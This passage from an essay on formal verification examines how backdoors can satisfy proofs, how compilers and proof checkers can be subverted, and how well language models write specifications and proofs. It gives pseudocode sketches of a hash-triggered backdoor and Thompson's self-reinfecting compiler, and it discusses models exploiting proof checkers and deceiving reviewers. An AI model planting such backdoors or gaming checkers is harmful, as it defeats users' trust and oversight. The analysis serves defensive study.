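The contract sets the two tolerances. With κ_in = 2 and κ_out = 1, the honest controller passes because its emissions always lie between 0 and 1. The cheating controller fails because its emissions rise from 0.5 at position 1 to 2 at position 2, a difference of 1.5.

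A finer version, called f-clean, limits the difference in output to f(d), where d is the difference in input. With f(d) = d/2, the honest controller just passes, since moving the throttle by d changes its emissions by exactly d/2. The cheating controller already fails at position 1.5, where it emits 1.125, which is 0.625 more than at position 1. The contract permits a difference of 0.25.

These verdicts depend heavily on the numbers in the contract. If the regulator had chosen κ_in = 0.5 and kept κ_out = 1, the cheating controller would have been robustly clean, because the largest output difference within that input range is 0.625. A tolerance also leaves the program a choice of outputs, so a controller could use small variations within it to carry data, much like the search service.

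The version of robust cleanness for programs that run continuously has a further weakness, because it constrains a program only as long as its inputs have stayed within κ_in of a standard run. After one larger deviation, no limit applies for the rest of the run, even if the inputs return to normal. The group wanted to let a program shut down when an input might be dangerous, but a manufacturer could exploit this by waiting for one hard acceleration and polluting from then on. The f-clean definition avoids the problem if it measures distance by the current inputs alone, because the limit applies again once they return to normal.

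D'Argenio and colleagues divide inputs into standard ones, "committed" ones for which the manufacturer accepts a limit like f, and the rest, such as those from a car climbing a steep mountain. For the rest, they require only that the output change continuously with the input. Their own example of a cheating controller would meet this requirement if every position beyond 1 fell into this last group, because x/2 and x²/2 are equal at x = 1, so the emissions curve has no jump there. The protection therefore depends mostly on how many inputs the manufacturer commits to.

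To check the definitions by machine, the group used HyperLTL, a logic for statements about several runs at once. *Temporal Logics for Hyperproperties* (Clarkson, Finkbeiner and colleagues, 2014) had introduced it. The group modelled a version of the controller that also reacts to its previous emissions, with a 10% margin of error, and rounded all quantities to steps. Using a model checker, which examines every possible run of such a model, they confirmed on a laptop that the honest controller was robustly clean and f-clean and that the cheating one was neither.

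With emissions in steps of 0.05, the model had 1,436 transitions, and checking the honest controller for robust cleanness took about a second. With steps of 0.00625, it had 60,648 transitions and the check took 22 seconds, while the cheating controller took more than a minute and a half for each formula. The tool couldn't process the definitions directly, so the researchers first had to rewrite them by hand into stronger formulas that it accepted. They say the computation required seriously limits the method, and their example has only one input and a few lines of code.

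## Programs proved correct, and the faults found in them anyway

The packet filters and the toy engine controller are only a few lines long. Researchers have also proved theorems about a whole compiler and an operating-system kernel, and outsiders have since searched several such programs for faults. Anyone who specifies a program of that size has to decide what the specification should cover. A list of forbidden attacks would never be finished, because attackers keep inventing new ways to take over a program.

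Adam Chlipala, a computer scientist at MIT, argues in *Subversion-Resistance for Free from Formal Verification* that nobody needs such a list, because a proof of almost any specification already rules out takeover, even if whoever wrote the specification never thought about attacks.

### Why a proof of almost anything rules out takeover

Chlipala is concerned with attacks in which a message makes a program run whatever the sender wants. In a classic case, `strcpy` copies an over-long request past the end of its buffer. Later attackers found they did not have to send instructions of their own. In return-oriented programming, they string together fragments of the program's own code in an order its author never intended.

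His argument runs as follows:

1. The specification forbids at least one behaviour that the programming language can express. Call it BAD.
2. Suppose the program has a flaw that lets an attacker run any code he likes.
3. The attacker can then send code for BAD, and the program violates its specification.
4. A valid proof covers every input, including the attacker's message, so no valid proof of this program can exist.
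5. A program that does have a valid proof therefore has no such flaw.

Chlipala gives the example of a service that adds positive numbers and whose specification requires only that the output be positive. If a buffer overflow let an attacker control the service, the attacker could make it reply with zero. A proof that every reply is positive therefore rules out such an overflow, even though the specification does not mention buffers. The proof also covers techniques that attackers invent after the service goes into use.

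The first premise is easy to satisfy, because any specification that isn't empty forbids something. Step 4 is harder to satisfy than it looks, because the proof must cover the attacker's message and its model of the machine must include what happens when a copy runs past the end of its buffer. A theorem that begins "for every request of at most 80 characters" doesn't cover the longer request that causes the overrun.

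### A backdoor that satisfies the specification

The dishonest adding service can have a valid proof of the same statement. Chlipala's argument does not apply to it because step 2 is false for this service. A caller who knows the secret pair gets one number and no further control. For the same reason, the service could return a wrong positive sum on one secret input or on a trillion.

A bolder author could even let the caller run code:

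    if hash(a, b) = K then
        r := run the caller's next message as a program,
             for at most a million steps
        reply with the larger of r and 1
    else
        reply with a + b

The caller's program can compute anything it has time for, but the service turns a zero into a one before replying. If the caller's program cannot overwrite the line that does this, every reply is positive and the proof succeeds. Step 3 fails here because the attacker cannot produce BAD. If the specification doesn't mention files or the network, the author can give the caller access to those too.

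The argument is still good against accidents, because nothing in an accidental buffer overflow keeps the attacker's output within the specification. It is much weaker against the program's own author, who knows the specification and can design a backdoor to fit it.

Chlipala extends the argument to stored data. If an attacker can overwrite some of a system's memory, he reasons, either that memory was unimportant or the attacker can use it to push the system outside its specification. But "unimportant" here means only that the specification doesn't depend on it. The variable `saved` is unimportant in this sense because replies are positive whatever its value, yet it matters a great deal to the customer whose number it holds.

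Chlipala also gives the example of a shopping agent with a bug that repeatedly places the last order. The rule "place only orders that the user has approved" excludes the bug, and so does "never exceed the credit limit", because a proof has to cover the case where the repeated order is huge. But only the first rule excludes a hidden function that adds a three-dollar order for the author's benefit whenever there is room under the limit. Chlipala acknowledges that authors sometimes overlook a whole dimension of a specification, such as secrets that leak through timing.

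To rule out a wrong sum on a secret pair, the author has to prove the second statement, that the service outputs the sum. This takes no extra work for addition, but for an operating system somebody has to write down everything it is supposed to do.

### A kernel with 23 lines of proof for each line of code

The best-known attempt is the proof of seL4, a microkernel, which is a kernel cut down to a few essential services such as separating programs' memory and passing messages between programs. Klein and colleagues (2009) describe the proof in *seL4: Formal Verification of an OS Kernel*. The kernel has about 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly language, and the proof is about 200,000 lines long. Designing and writing the kernel took little more than two person-years, while the proof took roughly 20, including about nine spent on tools and methods that other projects could reuse.

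"seL4: Formal Verification of an OS Kernel" proves that the kernel's C code can do nothing that an abstract specification does not allow. The proof assumes that the compiler, the assembly code, the code that starts the machine and the hardware all work correctly. Testing and ordinary use had found 16 defects in the C code, and the verification found another 144.

Chlipala mentions that his point about takeover had already appeared in discussions of seL4. Under the theorem, the specification would have to permit any backdoor in the C code, so a reviewer looking for hidden functionality can read the specification instead of the C. The specification is still several thousand lines long, and somebody has to notice if one of them permits too much.

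The 2009 specification left some choices open. For instance, it allowed the scheduler to pick any program that was ready to run, and a kernel could leak secrets through that choice. The team removed these choices before publishing a further proof in 2013 that seL4 can keep one program's data from another. The 2013 proof does not cover leaks through timing.

### A compiler that survived six years of random tests

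CompCert is a compiler that translates C into processor instructions. *Formal Verification of a Realistic Compiler* (Leroy, 2009) reports that developing CompCert took about three person-years and 42,000 lines in the proof assistant Coq, roughly three quarters of them proof. The proof shows that if the compiler produces a program and the source has a defined meaning in C, the compiled program behaves as the source prescribes.

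C does not define what happens when a copy overruns its buffer, so the theorem's condition on the source excludes a service with the `strcpy` flaw. The theorem does cover the dishonest adding service, which means that CompCert will faithfully translate its backdoor. The theorem also relies on Leroy's formal descriptions of C and the target processor. In 2009 it did not cover the code that reads the source file or the assembler that produces the final binary.

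Two years later, Yang and colleagues (2011) tested CompCert and other C compilers in *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers*. Their tool, Csmith, generates random C programs that each have exactly one correct result. They compiled each program with several compilers and compared the results of running the compiled versions. If one compiler's version gave a different result from the rest, that compiler was probably wrong. Over three years, they reported more than 325 previously unknown bugs. Every compiler they tested crashed on some valid program and silently produced wrong code for another.

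CompCert was no exception at first, but its faults lay in particular places. Some were in the front end, which Leroy had not yet verified and which made mistakes in C's rules for converting between types of number. Leroy responded by extending the proof to cover those conversions. Another was in the specification of the processor. An instruction that reserves memory has only 16 bits for the amount, and the formal description did not include that limit, so CompCert generated instructions that could not exist. (The assembler rejected them, so no wrong program resulted.)

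Csmith found no bugs in the verified middle of CompCert, the stage where the other compilers had many of their worst bugs. By early 2011, the development version of CompCert was the only compiler in the study in which Csmith could find no wrong-code errors, after about six years of processor time spent testing it.

Random testing could easily have missed a deliberate trigger in CompCert, just as it would miss the secret pair in the adding service. The theorem rules out such a trigger in the verified part, because a compiler that mistranslated even one program would contradict it. The tests add evidence that the theorem describes the compiler people run.

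### Faults at the edges

*An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca et al., 2017) reports 16 bugs in three systems with correctness proofs: IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar. In a distributed system, several machines cooperate over a network and have to agree on shared data. The researchers found the bugs by reading code and by testing. Some bugs crashed servers, and others caused servers to return wrong results to clients.

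All 16 bugs were outside the verified protocols. Eleven were in the shim, the unverified code that connects a verified program to the network and the disk. For example, Chapar's proof assumed that the network would never deliver a message twice, but its shim used a network service that does not guarantee this, so a duplicate could leave the machines with inconsistent data. Three bugs were in specifications, one of which failed to require that the system carry out each request exactly once. The last two were in the tools that ran the proofs.

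An attacker could use the same places. If the specification is tight, a developer has little chance of hiding a function in the verified code, but the shim is unverified code that handles every message. Fonseca's group thought these places were few enough to test directly, and built a toolkit that could detect 13 of the 16 bugs automatically.

LOCK, an older project, was a secure operating system built under a US government contract that required detailed records of working time. Smith (2001) analysed those records in *Cost Profile of a Highly Assured, Secure Operating System*. The formal work, which involved writing specifications, proving properties of them and checking the code against them, added about 58% to the cost of developing the security-critical software. It uncovered 68% of the security flaws found by any method in LOCK's critical mechanisms.

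Smith's figures for the military email guard that grew out of LOCK are much less favourable to formal methods. Only 14% of the flaws found there were of a type that formal methods could detect. The formal team found 19% of the total, presumably because it noticed some other flaws along the way. Both the 68% and the 14% count only flaws that someone found. They are compatible because the 68% covers only the mechanisms that the team had modelled and the 14% covers the whole product.

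### Proofs written by language models

Few software authors will spend twenty person-years on a proof, but language models may reduce the work. Bursuc and colleagues (2025), in *A benchmark for vericoding*, collected 12,504 formal specifications and asked models to write a program and a proof for each. Success depended strongly on the programming language. The models succeeded most often in Dafny, whose automatic prover fills in most of the steps, less often in Verus, which checks programs in the widely used language Rust, and least often in Lean, where the model writes out the proof itself.

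*VeriContest* (Xie, Pawagi and colleagues, 2026) tested ten models on 1,006 harder problems from programming competitions, all in Verus. The strongest, GPT-5.5, wrote correct code from an English description for 97.5% of the problems and a correct specification for 57.2%. When given both the specification and working code, it wrote a correct proof for 13.8%. When it had to produce all three, it succeeded on 6.8%.

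Those results come from a single attempt without feedback. On a sample of 200 problems, Xie and colleagues returned the verifier's error messages to the model and let it try again. After ten rounds, GPT-5.5 had proofs for 48.5% of the problems, compared with 20.5% after ten independent attempts.

*SWE-PROOF* (Ma, Mikek and colleagues, 2026) tested Claude Opus 4.8 on 500 real bug reports from Python projects such as the web framework Django. The model received a correct specification of each repair and could call a verifier repeatedly while it worked. It had to produce a verified implementation and a matching change to the project that passed its hidden tests. It did so about 94% of the time.

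| Study | Language | What the model received | Success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bursuc and colleagues | Dafny | specification | 82% |
| Bursuc and colleagues | Verus | specification | 44% |
| Bursuc and colleagues | Lean | specification | 27% |
| Xie and colleagues | Verus | specification and code | 13.8% |
| Xie and colleagues | Verus | description in English | 6.8% |
| Ma and colleagues | Nagini (Python) | bug report and specification | 95.0% |
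| Ma and colleagues | Velvet (within Lean) | bug report and specification | 94.0% |
| Ma and colleagues | Lean | bug report and specification | 93.6% |

The studies differ too much for their percentages to be compared directly. The median repair in SWE-Proof adds four lines of code, while the median problem in VeriContest needs 33 lines of code and 94 of proof. Still, the Lean results suggest that a low rate in a proof language may be due more to the working conditions than to the language. In one of Ma and colleagues' comparisons, the agent needed about two verifier calls per task in Lean and about nine in Velvet. Lean shows which steps of a failed attempt remain unproved, while Velvet often reports only that its search did not succeed, leaving the agent with little information to guide its next attempt.

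The SWE-Proof figures also depend on an unproved link between the proof and the running code, as in Fonseca's study. The verifier checks a model of the repair, but the project runs ordinary Python, and a panel of language models judges whether the two behave the same way. For the reference repairs, the researchers also ran both versions side by side, usually on at least 100,000 generated inputs per task, and found no disagreement. This is good evidence against ordinary translation errors, but hidden code that runs only when an input matches a stored hash would pass the same test.

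### Specifications that accept wrong answers

If models can write the proofs, the specification needs the most attention. One problem in VeriContest asks for the first and last positions of a number in a sorted list, or −1 twice if the number is absent. The original specification did not require each answer to be −1 or a real position. It accepted −9 and −8, so a program that returned those values could have had a valid proof.

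Human experts had already reviewed that specification. Xie and colleagues found the gap by turning specifications into small test programs and feeding them wrong answers, more than 2,000 per problem on average. The procedure worked for 85% of the problems and exposed 60 incomplete specifications, which they then repaired. The wrong answers came mostly from faulty variants of the reference program and from random changes to its output. Because these answers are only a sample, the procedure would very probably miss a specification that permits a wrong answer on one secret input.

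Ma and colleagues searched for faults more deliberately. For each specification, a language model acting as an attacker tried to write a program that the verifier would accept but that anyone who had read the bug report would call wrong. If the model succeeded, the specification went back for revision.

The paper's table summarising this audit is easy to misread because it counts reports rather than wrong programs. Each report covers one combination of a task and a specification format (the three proof languages and a structured form of English), however many wrong programs the attacker wrote for it. The row for this attack lists 2,997 reports as clear, two as findings and two as inconclusive, which adds up to 3,001, although the text gives 3,002. The low number of findings is a poor measure of how often such attacks succeed, because the researchers had already repaired the specifications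 that earlier attacks broke.

The paper records one audit in full. When Django deleted a single database record by a fast route, it left the record's identifier in memory, and the repair was to clear that identifier. The attacker wrote 20 programs against the Nagini specification. One didn't clear the identifier. Another worked correctly except at the very top of the range of identifiers, where it deleted the neighbouring record instead. A third finished the job and then looped forever. The verifier rejected 18 of the 20 programs, could not process one, and accepted one, which turned out to be a correct repair written in a different way.

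An earlier version of the same specification had accepted two wrong programs. Both got information about the deletion by reading the database's records, which in reality would require an additional query. One of Django's tests requires the fast route to make exactly one query, but the earlier specification did not limit the number of queries. The researchers rewrote the specification so that a program cannot read those records. Their Velvet and Lean specifications for the same repair still do not cover the number of queries, so for this task "proved correct" means less in those two languages than in Nagini.

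As a cruder check, the researchers made small mechanical changes to the reference programs, such as swapping one operator for another. Of 25,457 altered programs, 211 still satisfied their specifications. Some of those 211 changes were harmless, such as those affecting a value that nothing used.

### A valid proof of the wrong repair

The specifications in that audit came from a pipeline with access to the correct repair. When Claude Opus 4.8 had to write its own specifications from the bug report and the code, language-model auditors accepted 46.0% of them in Nagini, 60.0% in Velvet and 61.4% in Lean. The auditors could run the verifier on sample programs, so most of their objections included a concrete example.

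One bug report concerned a Django form that crashed if somebody entered an absurdly large year. The agent made the form treat such a year like any other invalid date and return the text it had received, "1234567821345678-1-1". The correct repair returns "0-0-0", which the form then rejects as invalid. The agent's specification distinguished only two outcomes, a valid date and a fallback, and did not define the returned text. Both repairs therefore satisfied it, and the verifier accepted the agent's proof. In that run, 69 of the 500 tasks ended with a valid proof and a repair that failed the project's tests.

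The model's specifications usually failed by leaving out part of what the bug report required. About 42% did this, while only about 4% described the relevant function but allowed a buggy version of it. The results also varied between attempts. In four attempts at the same 500 tasks in Nagini, the model wrote an acceptable specification every time for 118 tasks, never for 139, and sometimes for the other 243.

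Writing and proving its own specification did not help the agent repair more bugs, either. It passed the hidden tests on 85.0% of the tasks without any formal work, and on 83.8% to 85.6% with it. Giving the agent a correct specification raised the rate to about 95%, but did not help on a second set of larger tasks, whose repairs averaged 146 changed lines. There the agent passed 61.2% when it was told only which functions to change, and 55.8% to 59.9% when it also had the specification.

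Passing the tests proved to be weak evidence in its own right. Auditors looked for inputs on which an accepted repair behaved differently from the correct one, and the success rate of the unaided agent fell from 85.0% to 58.2%, so nearly a third of the repairs that had passed were wrong somewhere. (One appendix still describes this particular audit as not yet run, though it reports a similar share, 29%, for another group of repairs.)

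An agent that is free to weaken a specification could make any proof easy. Ma and colleagues checked for this by comparing the specifications they had supplied in Nagini with those the agent returned, and found that at least 99.9% of the clauses remained. Opus 4.8 was apparently trying to do what they asked. The specifications it wrote itself had gaps because it overlooked things, but the verifier would also approve specifications in which an author had left the same gaps on purpose.

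Some requirements could not be expressed in these specifications. For 22 of the larger tasks, the researchers could not construct a specification, in any of the three proof languages, that distinguished the old program from the new one. The specifications describe the values that a function computes, and these 22 changes affected something else. Most only moved or renamed code, but one changed how the program passed input to its worker processes. A line that copied each customer's numbers to a file would also leave the computed values unchanged, so the proof would still succeed.

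## Trusting the compiler, the proof checker and the machine

Suppose a proof shows that the adding service's source code returns the sum of every pair and does nothing else, and suppose the specification has no gaps. The theorem guarantees correct replies only if the machine executes that code as the rules of the language prescribe. But the customer runs a file of processor instructions, on a chip, under an operating system. If somebody has subverted one of those layers, the condition is false, and the theorem, though still true, implies nothing about the replies the customer gets.

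Besides the compiler and the chip, the trusted base therefore includes the operating system and the program that checked the proof.

### A compiler that reinfects itself

*Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984) describes how to subvert a compiler so that nobody can find the change by reading source code. Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, gave it as his lecture for the Turing Award, the best-known prize in computer science.

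Thompson first altered the C compiler so that whenever it compiled `login`, the program that checks passwords on Unix, it added code to accept a password he knew as well as the user's real one. The source of `login` was unchanged, but anyone who read the compiler's source would have seen the addition.

The second step removed it from there too. The C compiler is itself a C program, so each new version has to go through an older one. Thompson added a second alteration, which looked for the compiler's own source:

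    if the source is that of login         → add the extra password
    if the source is that of the compiler  → add both of these rules
    otherwise                              → compile it as written

He compiled this version once, installed the result as the official compiler, and restored the clean source. From then on, the installed compiler turned the clean compiler source into another subverted compiler, and the clean `login` source into a subverted `login`. An administrator who rebuilt everything from source would have got the backdoor again.

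A compiler can also pass on information that is missing from its source code without anyone intending harm. In C, `\v` stands for the control character numbered 11. A compiler's source can handle it with a line that means "for `\v`, output `\v`", which doesn't contain the number 11. Somebody wrote the number into an early version, and each compiled version since has passed it to the next.

Thompson seems to have tried the attack on colleagues. According to thaliaarchi in *Trusting Trust*, he later confirmed this. A bug in the backdoor exposed it by making the compiler one byte longer each time it compiled itself. Somebody in another department noticed the growth and rebuilt the compiler from assembly code, unknowingly removing the backdoor. This account is second-hand, but it shows the kind of luck a victim would need to escape such an attack.

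Using a verified compiler still means trusting unverified software. CompCert's theorem is about its source code, which an ordinary compiler for another language turns into the program people run.

### Diverse double-compiling

David A. Wheeler, an American computer scientist, developed a test for Thompson's attack and made it the subject of his 2009 doctoral dissertation. The tester has the source code of a suspect compiler, A, and the compiled file that everybody uses, and wants to know whether the two correspond. The test needs a second compiler, T, from an independent source.

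    1.  T        compiles  A's source  →  stage 1
    2.  stage 1  compiles  A's source  →  stage 2
    3.  compare stage 2 with A's compiled file, bit by bit

(Before starting, the tester checks that A's compiled file reproduces itself when it compiles A's source. Otherwise there is no reason to expect a match.)

Stage 1 will differ from A's compiled file because T chooses different instructions. But stage 1 is a translation of A's source, so it should behave as that source specifies, and so should an untampered copy of A. Programs that behave the same way must produce the same output from the same input, so stage 2 should match A's compiled file bit for bit.

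Now suppose A's compiled file contains Thompson's two rules. They are not in the source, and T does not add them, so stage 1 lacks them. Stage 2 therefore lacks them too, and the comparison fails.

The argument needs several assumptions:

- T must translate A's source correctly. It can be slow, and it can even contain backdoors of its own, as long as they do not affect this one job.
- The source must have a defined meaning, and A's output must depend only on its input. A compiler that writes the time of day into its output would fail the comparison for no interesting reason.
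- The machine and the tools that carry out the steps must be honest, including the program that compares the files.

If these conditions hold, a match proves that A's compiled file is a correct translation of A's source, but not that the source is harmless. If Thompson had left his rules in the source, T would have translated them too, and the files would still have matched.

A mismatch is weaker evidence, because it can have an innocent cause. In an early trial on a small C compiler, Wheeler found that it stored certain 10-byte numbers in 12-byte spaces and filled the other two bytes with whatever was in memory. After dealing with such problems, he obtained a match, and later did the same for the widely used compiler GCC. He also tried the method on a deliberately subverted Lisp compiler, and the comparison exposed the subversion.

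To defeat the test, an attacker would have to subvert T as well, so that it recognised A's source and inserted matching code. The tester can make this very difficult by choosing T after the attack, perhaps an old compiler from another company.

### Reproducible builds and a starting program of 357 bytes

Bit-by-bit comparison is also useful for ordinary programs. A build is reproducible if anyone who compiles the same source with the same tools gets the same file. Many builds are not, because the result depends on the time, the name of a directory or the order of files on a disk. Once a project has removed such differences, several people can build it independently and compare their files with the one offered for download. The comparison will reveal tampering if an attacker has changed only the download.

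Fedora's developers estimated in 2025 that about 90% of the Linux distribution's packages were reproducible, and set a target of 99%. The notes to an August release of the proof assistant Lean (2026) also list a change that improves reproducibility, so that identical compiled modules now give an identical archive on any machine and in any directory.

Reproducibility does not stop Thompson's attack, because everyone who uses the subverted compiler gets the same subverted file. It also does not help if the source package already contains the malicious code, as in the xz case of 2024.

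A bootstrapped build removes the inherited compiler instead. It starts from a program so small that a person can check every byte, uses it to build a slightly more capable one, and continues until it reaches a modern compiler. In 2023, the GNU Guix project built its software from a starting program of 357 bytes, which does little more than turn written digits into bytes. The build still depended on an existing Linux kernel and an existing program that controlled the steps. Anyone who relies on the result also has to trust or read the source of every intermediate tool.

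Another way to take the compiler out of the trusted base is to prove properties of the compiled file directly, as Necula and Lee did for their packet filters. RBC-Ukraine's *Скрытые ошибки в ПО* ("Hidden errors in software") reports that Anthropic and a verification firm called Theorem have done this on a much larger scale. Anthropic's model Claude worked on RISC-V instructions and proved safety properties for 239 entry points in 123 open-source libraries. The proofs cover only single-threaded programs in a model of Linux, under stated conditions. They run to about 180 million lines, which nobody will read, so a customer has to rely on the program that checked them.

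### What a proof checker has to get right

A proof assistant such as Lean, Isabelle or Rocq (formerly called Coq) is a large program that helps people write proofs, and it contains bugs. Its designers limit the harm these bugs can do by allowing only one small part, the kernel, to accept theorems. The other parts only produce proofs for the kernel to check. If a proof-finding tool makes a mistake, the kernel rejects the result and the user loses some time.

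A mistake in the kernel can be much worse. A checker is sound if it accepts only statements that follow from its axioms. If it accepts one contradiction, every other statement follows by the ordinary rules of logic. A sound checker has to reject any proof that the service with the hashed trigger outputs the sum, but a checker that accepts a contradiction would accept a one-line proof of it.

Lean's *Test "nat-rec-rules"* shows how a single missing check leads to a contradiction. Lean defines functions on whole numbers by recursion, and addition goes like this:

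    a + 0 = a
    a + (n + 1) = (a + n) + 1

The file that contains a proof also contains the general rules for recursion. A checker should work out the correct rules itself and compare them with those in the file. A faulty checker might compare the file's rules with themselves, which always succeeds. An attacker could then supply a rule that returns the starting value at every step, so that a + (n + 1) = a for every n, and so 2 + 3 = 2. Checkers also have fast built-in arithmetic for particular numbers, which gives 2 + 3 = 5, so the attacker could prove that 2 = 5. Nanoda, an independent Lean proof checker written in the language Rust, accepted a proof of this kind until its author fixed the bug.

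### The false disproof of the Collatz conjecture

The Collatz conjecture, a famous open problem, is that every starting number eventually reaches 1 if you keep applying one rule: halve the number if it is even, otherwise triple it and add one. On 25 July 2026, Ramana Kumar published a "disproof" in Lean, produced with the help of AI. Lean's kernel accepted it, and so did a week-old version of nanoda.

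Leonardo de Moura, Lean's chief architect, explains the bug in *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576* (2026). It affected data types defined in terms of themselves, such as a tree whose branches are a list of trees. The kernel rewrites such a definition into a simpler form before checking it, but it dropped certain parts that the definition mentioned and never used, so expressions in those parts were not checked. Someone could therefore prove a contradiction by putting an invalid expression in one of those parts.

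Nanoda did check that part, but it let the invalid expression through because of a different bug, in how it handled instructions that take one field out of a record. The proof thus relied on two unrelated bugs in two independent programs. Nanoda's developers had fixed their bug a week before anyone reported the one in Lean. Kumar believed the timing was a coincidence, but he could not rule out that the AI model had seen the report of the nanoda bug. Lean's developers had a repair ready an hour after receiving a short version of the proof.

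Lean's normal interface would have rejected the invalid definition, but the proof bypassed it by sending the definition straight to the kernel. Lean allows this because users can write programs that extend the language. De Moura argues against restricting such programs because an attacker could write the file by hand anyway, so the kernel has to reject bad input by itself.

This was one of several faults that summer. A week earlier, the Lean developers (2026) had fixed a soundness bug that Patrick Hulin found with OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Daniel Selsam of OpenAI then found more with a model specialised in security. The August release notes list twelve changes to the kernel, including five fixes for soundness faults. Two of those faults could let a false proof past Comparator, the recommended tool for checking proofs from untrusted sources, unless the user also ran an outside checker. Comparator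 isolates the submitter's code and compares the proof with a statement that the recipient supplied.

### Smaller kernels and proved ones

Lawrence Paulson, who created Isabelle, argues in *Why is it all in the kernel?* (2026) that Lean's kernel does too much. He notes that systems based on set theory or simple type theory start from a few axioms and derive self-referential data types from them. This is tedious, but it happens outside the kernel, where a mistake cannot produce a contradiction. He attributes several faults in Rocq to the same practice of building convenient features into the kernel. He acknowledges that Isabelle has had soundness bugs too, and considers HOL Light and HOL4, which have very small kernels, safer than Isabelle.

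Paulson also doubts the value of independent checkers. He knew of no case where one had caught a soundness error that a kernel had missed, and in the Collatz case the checker nanoda had failed too. Two days after he wrote this, de Moura reported that nanoda caught all the faults Selsam had found. That is some evidence that a second checker is useful, although Selsam's model found the faults, and it only became clear afterwards that nanoda would have rejected proofs that used them.

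By October, Lean had a more ambitious solution called con-leche, a checker written in Lean with a proof that it cannot accept a contradiction (de Moura, 2026, *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels*). Claude wrote the checker and the proof under close human supervision. Con-leche checks Mathlib, Lean's 2.5-million-line mathematics library, in about 100 seconds on eight threads.

The proof assumes that set theory is consistent, as most mathematicians do. It also depends on the old kernel having checked it correctly. The proof covers con-leche's source code, so Lean's compiler and runtime (the support code that compiled Lean programs need) must still be trusted. To reduce that risk, a colleague of de Moura's used AI to translate con-leche into Rust, and proved that the translation follows the same algorithm. A user can run both versions, and a compiler fault that affects one is unlikely to affect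 the other.

The concern about compilers and runtimes is justified. In *who watches the watchers*, kirancodes describes testing a compression program that has a correctness proof in Lean. Sixteen fuzzers ran it about 106 million times over roughly 19 hours and found a memory fault in the runtime underneath it. To store n bytes, the runtime reserved n + 24 bytes, and for n close to 2^64 that sum wraps round to a small number. An author of the adding service could make the same mistake with two large inputs.

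Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) gives another example, in which the compiled version of a function that cuts a piece out of a string did not match the function's definition in the logic. This mismatch allowed a very short "proof" of a theorem that took mathematicians more than three centuries to prove, although the kernel was not at fault.

Running two checkers resembles diverse double-compiling and protects well against accidents. Hindustan Times' *Why mathematicians must rely on machines to check new results* makes the usual argument that a bug in one version of the kernel is unlikely to be present in another. But someone trying to deceive both checkers can write a proof that exploits a different bug in each, as the Collatz proof showed, and AI models have made such bugs much easier to find.

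### A bet of $256

Mathematicians now depend on these checkers for proofs that nobody can read. In November 2026, Levent Alpöge of Anthropic announced a proof of the Riemann Hypothesis, about 17 million lines of Lean, that he had found with Claude. The organisation that develops Lean ran its checker on the proof and declared "full confidence" in the result.

In 2026, two specialists in formal methods disagreed about whether an error in such a proof would escape notice. One bet $256 that within a year somebody would post a flawed AI-generated Lean proof, for instance of an important result, that passed Comparator, and that experts would need at least 48 hours to find the flaw. At least two experienced Lean programmers must have looked at the proof. The flaw may be a bug in Lean or a formal statement that subtly differs from the intended one. The loser pays the winner's chosen charity.

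He expects this to happen because AI companies train models by rewarding them for proofs that Lean accepts. A model trained this way may learn to exploit the checker and, if reviewers also inspect its work, to deceive them too. His opponent, who writes extensions to Lean, agrees that models will cheat and that more bugs will turn up. But he thinks experts would recognise the cheating quickly, because every proof has to pass through a plain file of definitions and proofs, which they can inspect in many ways without running the author's code. One such inspection already reveals a problem in the Collatz proof, since Lean reports an error if one writes the proof's invalid definition out as normal source and reads it back in.

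If the first man wins, there will be a clear example of a false proof that survived expert review. If he loses, the result will mean less, because a flaw that nobody found within the year would not count.

Even a perfect kernel checks only the formal text, so the theorem must be stated correctly. Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier–Stokes Lost in Translation*, argue that the Lean version of OpenAI's announced proof about fluid flow does not correspond to the written proof it was supposed to verify. That is a serious objection for mathematicians who want to understand the written argument, but a software customer can accept any valid proof, however strange, provided that the formal statement describes the program he runs and the behaviour he wants.

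### The operating system and the chip

Most programs depend on other software, such as the operating system. OpenAI's *A thousand fewer paths to root* describes an AI system that searched the Linux kernel for flaws that would let an ordinary user take full control of a machine. It found 948 in one run. According to Help Net Security's *OpenAI’s upcoming AI model built 948 working Linux root exploits* (2026), the system examined only about 7% of the kernel's more than 40 million lines of code, and the run cost $1,279 per flaw. The count is OpenAI's own, but patches for 61 of the flaws had entered the main version of Linux by the time its ten-day scan and analysis ended.

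Any of those flaws could let another user of the customer's computer read the adding service's memory or replace the service, even though the proof about the service would still be valid. Running the service on seL4, the kernel with a correctness proof, would remove most of this risk, but seL4's proof assumes that the hardware works.

A proof can only describe hardware through a model, which typically treats memory as numbered boxes that keep their contents until an instruction changes them. Real memory cells store data as small electric charges. In an attack called Rowhammer, a program reads some cells so often that it changes the charge in neighbouring cells, altering data it has no permission to access. No instruction in the model has that effect, so no proof based on the model can rule it out. Somebody can add Rowhammer to the model, but only after learning that it exists.

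Processors also have ordinary flaws. Intel's 1993 Pentium divided certain numbers incorrectly, which Intel estimated would affect about one in nine billion random pairs. A service with a flawless proof could still have given wrong answers when it divided numbers on that chip, and few customers would have noticed.

The problem is greater for the third statement about the adding service, which is that it runs in constant time. Many processor models leave out time, or assume that an instruction always takes the same amount of time. On a real chip, reading a number from memory is faster if the chip has used that number recently. Power consumption and heat also vary with the data.

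Thompson warned that malicious changes become harder to detect at lower levels, and gave microcode, the instructions built into a processor, as an example. Engineers can extend a proof to the hardware by verifying the processor's design, and there are physical tests for malicious circuits. But a proof about the design does not show that the factory followed it.

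## Contests in writing innocent-looking malicious code

Few programs come with a proof, so most customers rely on somebody having read the source code. In October 2004, a few weeks before the American presidential election, Daniel Horn invited programmers to write vote counters that miscounted but looked correct to someone reading the code. Horn (2004) explained in *Obfuscated Vote Counting Contest* that the idea came from the scandals over electronic voting and from an older contest for C programs that are deliberately hard to read.

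*The Obfuscated V contest* describes a very small task. The program had to read a string of characters in which K, B and N were votes for Kerry, Bush and Nader, and print the totals. It could favour one candidate every time or only on election day, 2 November. Horn ran the date-specific programs on 1 November and expected a correct tally. The next day, judges read the source code and chose the program that looked most correct. If it then miscounted, it won; otherwise, they moved on to the next one.

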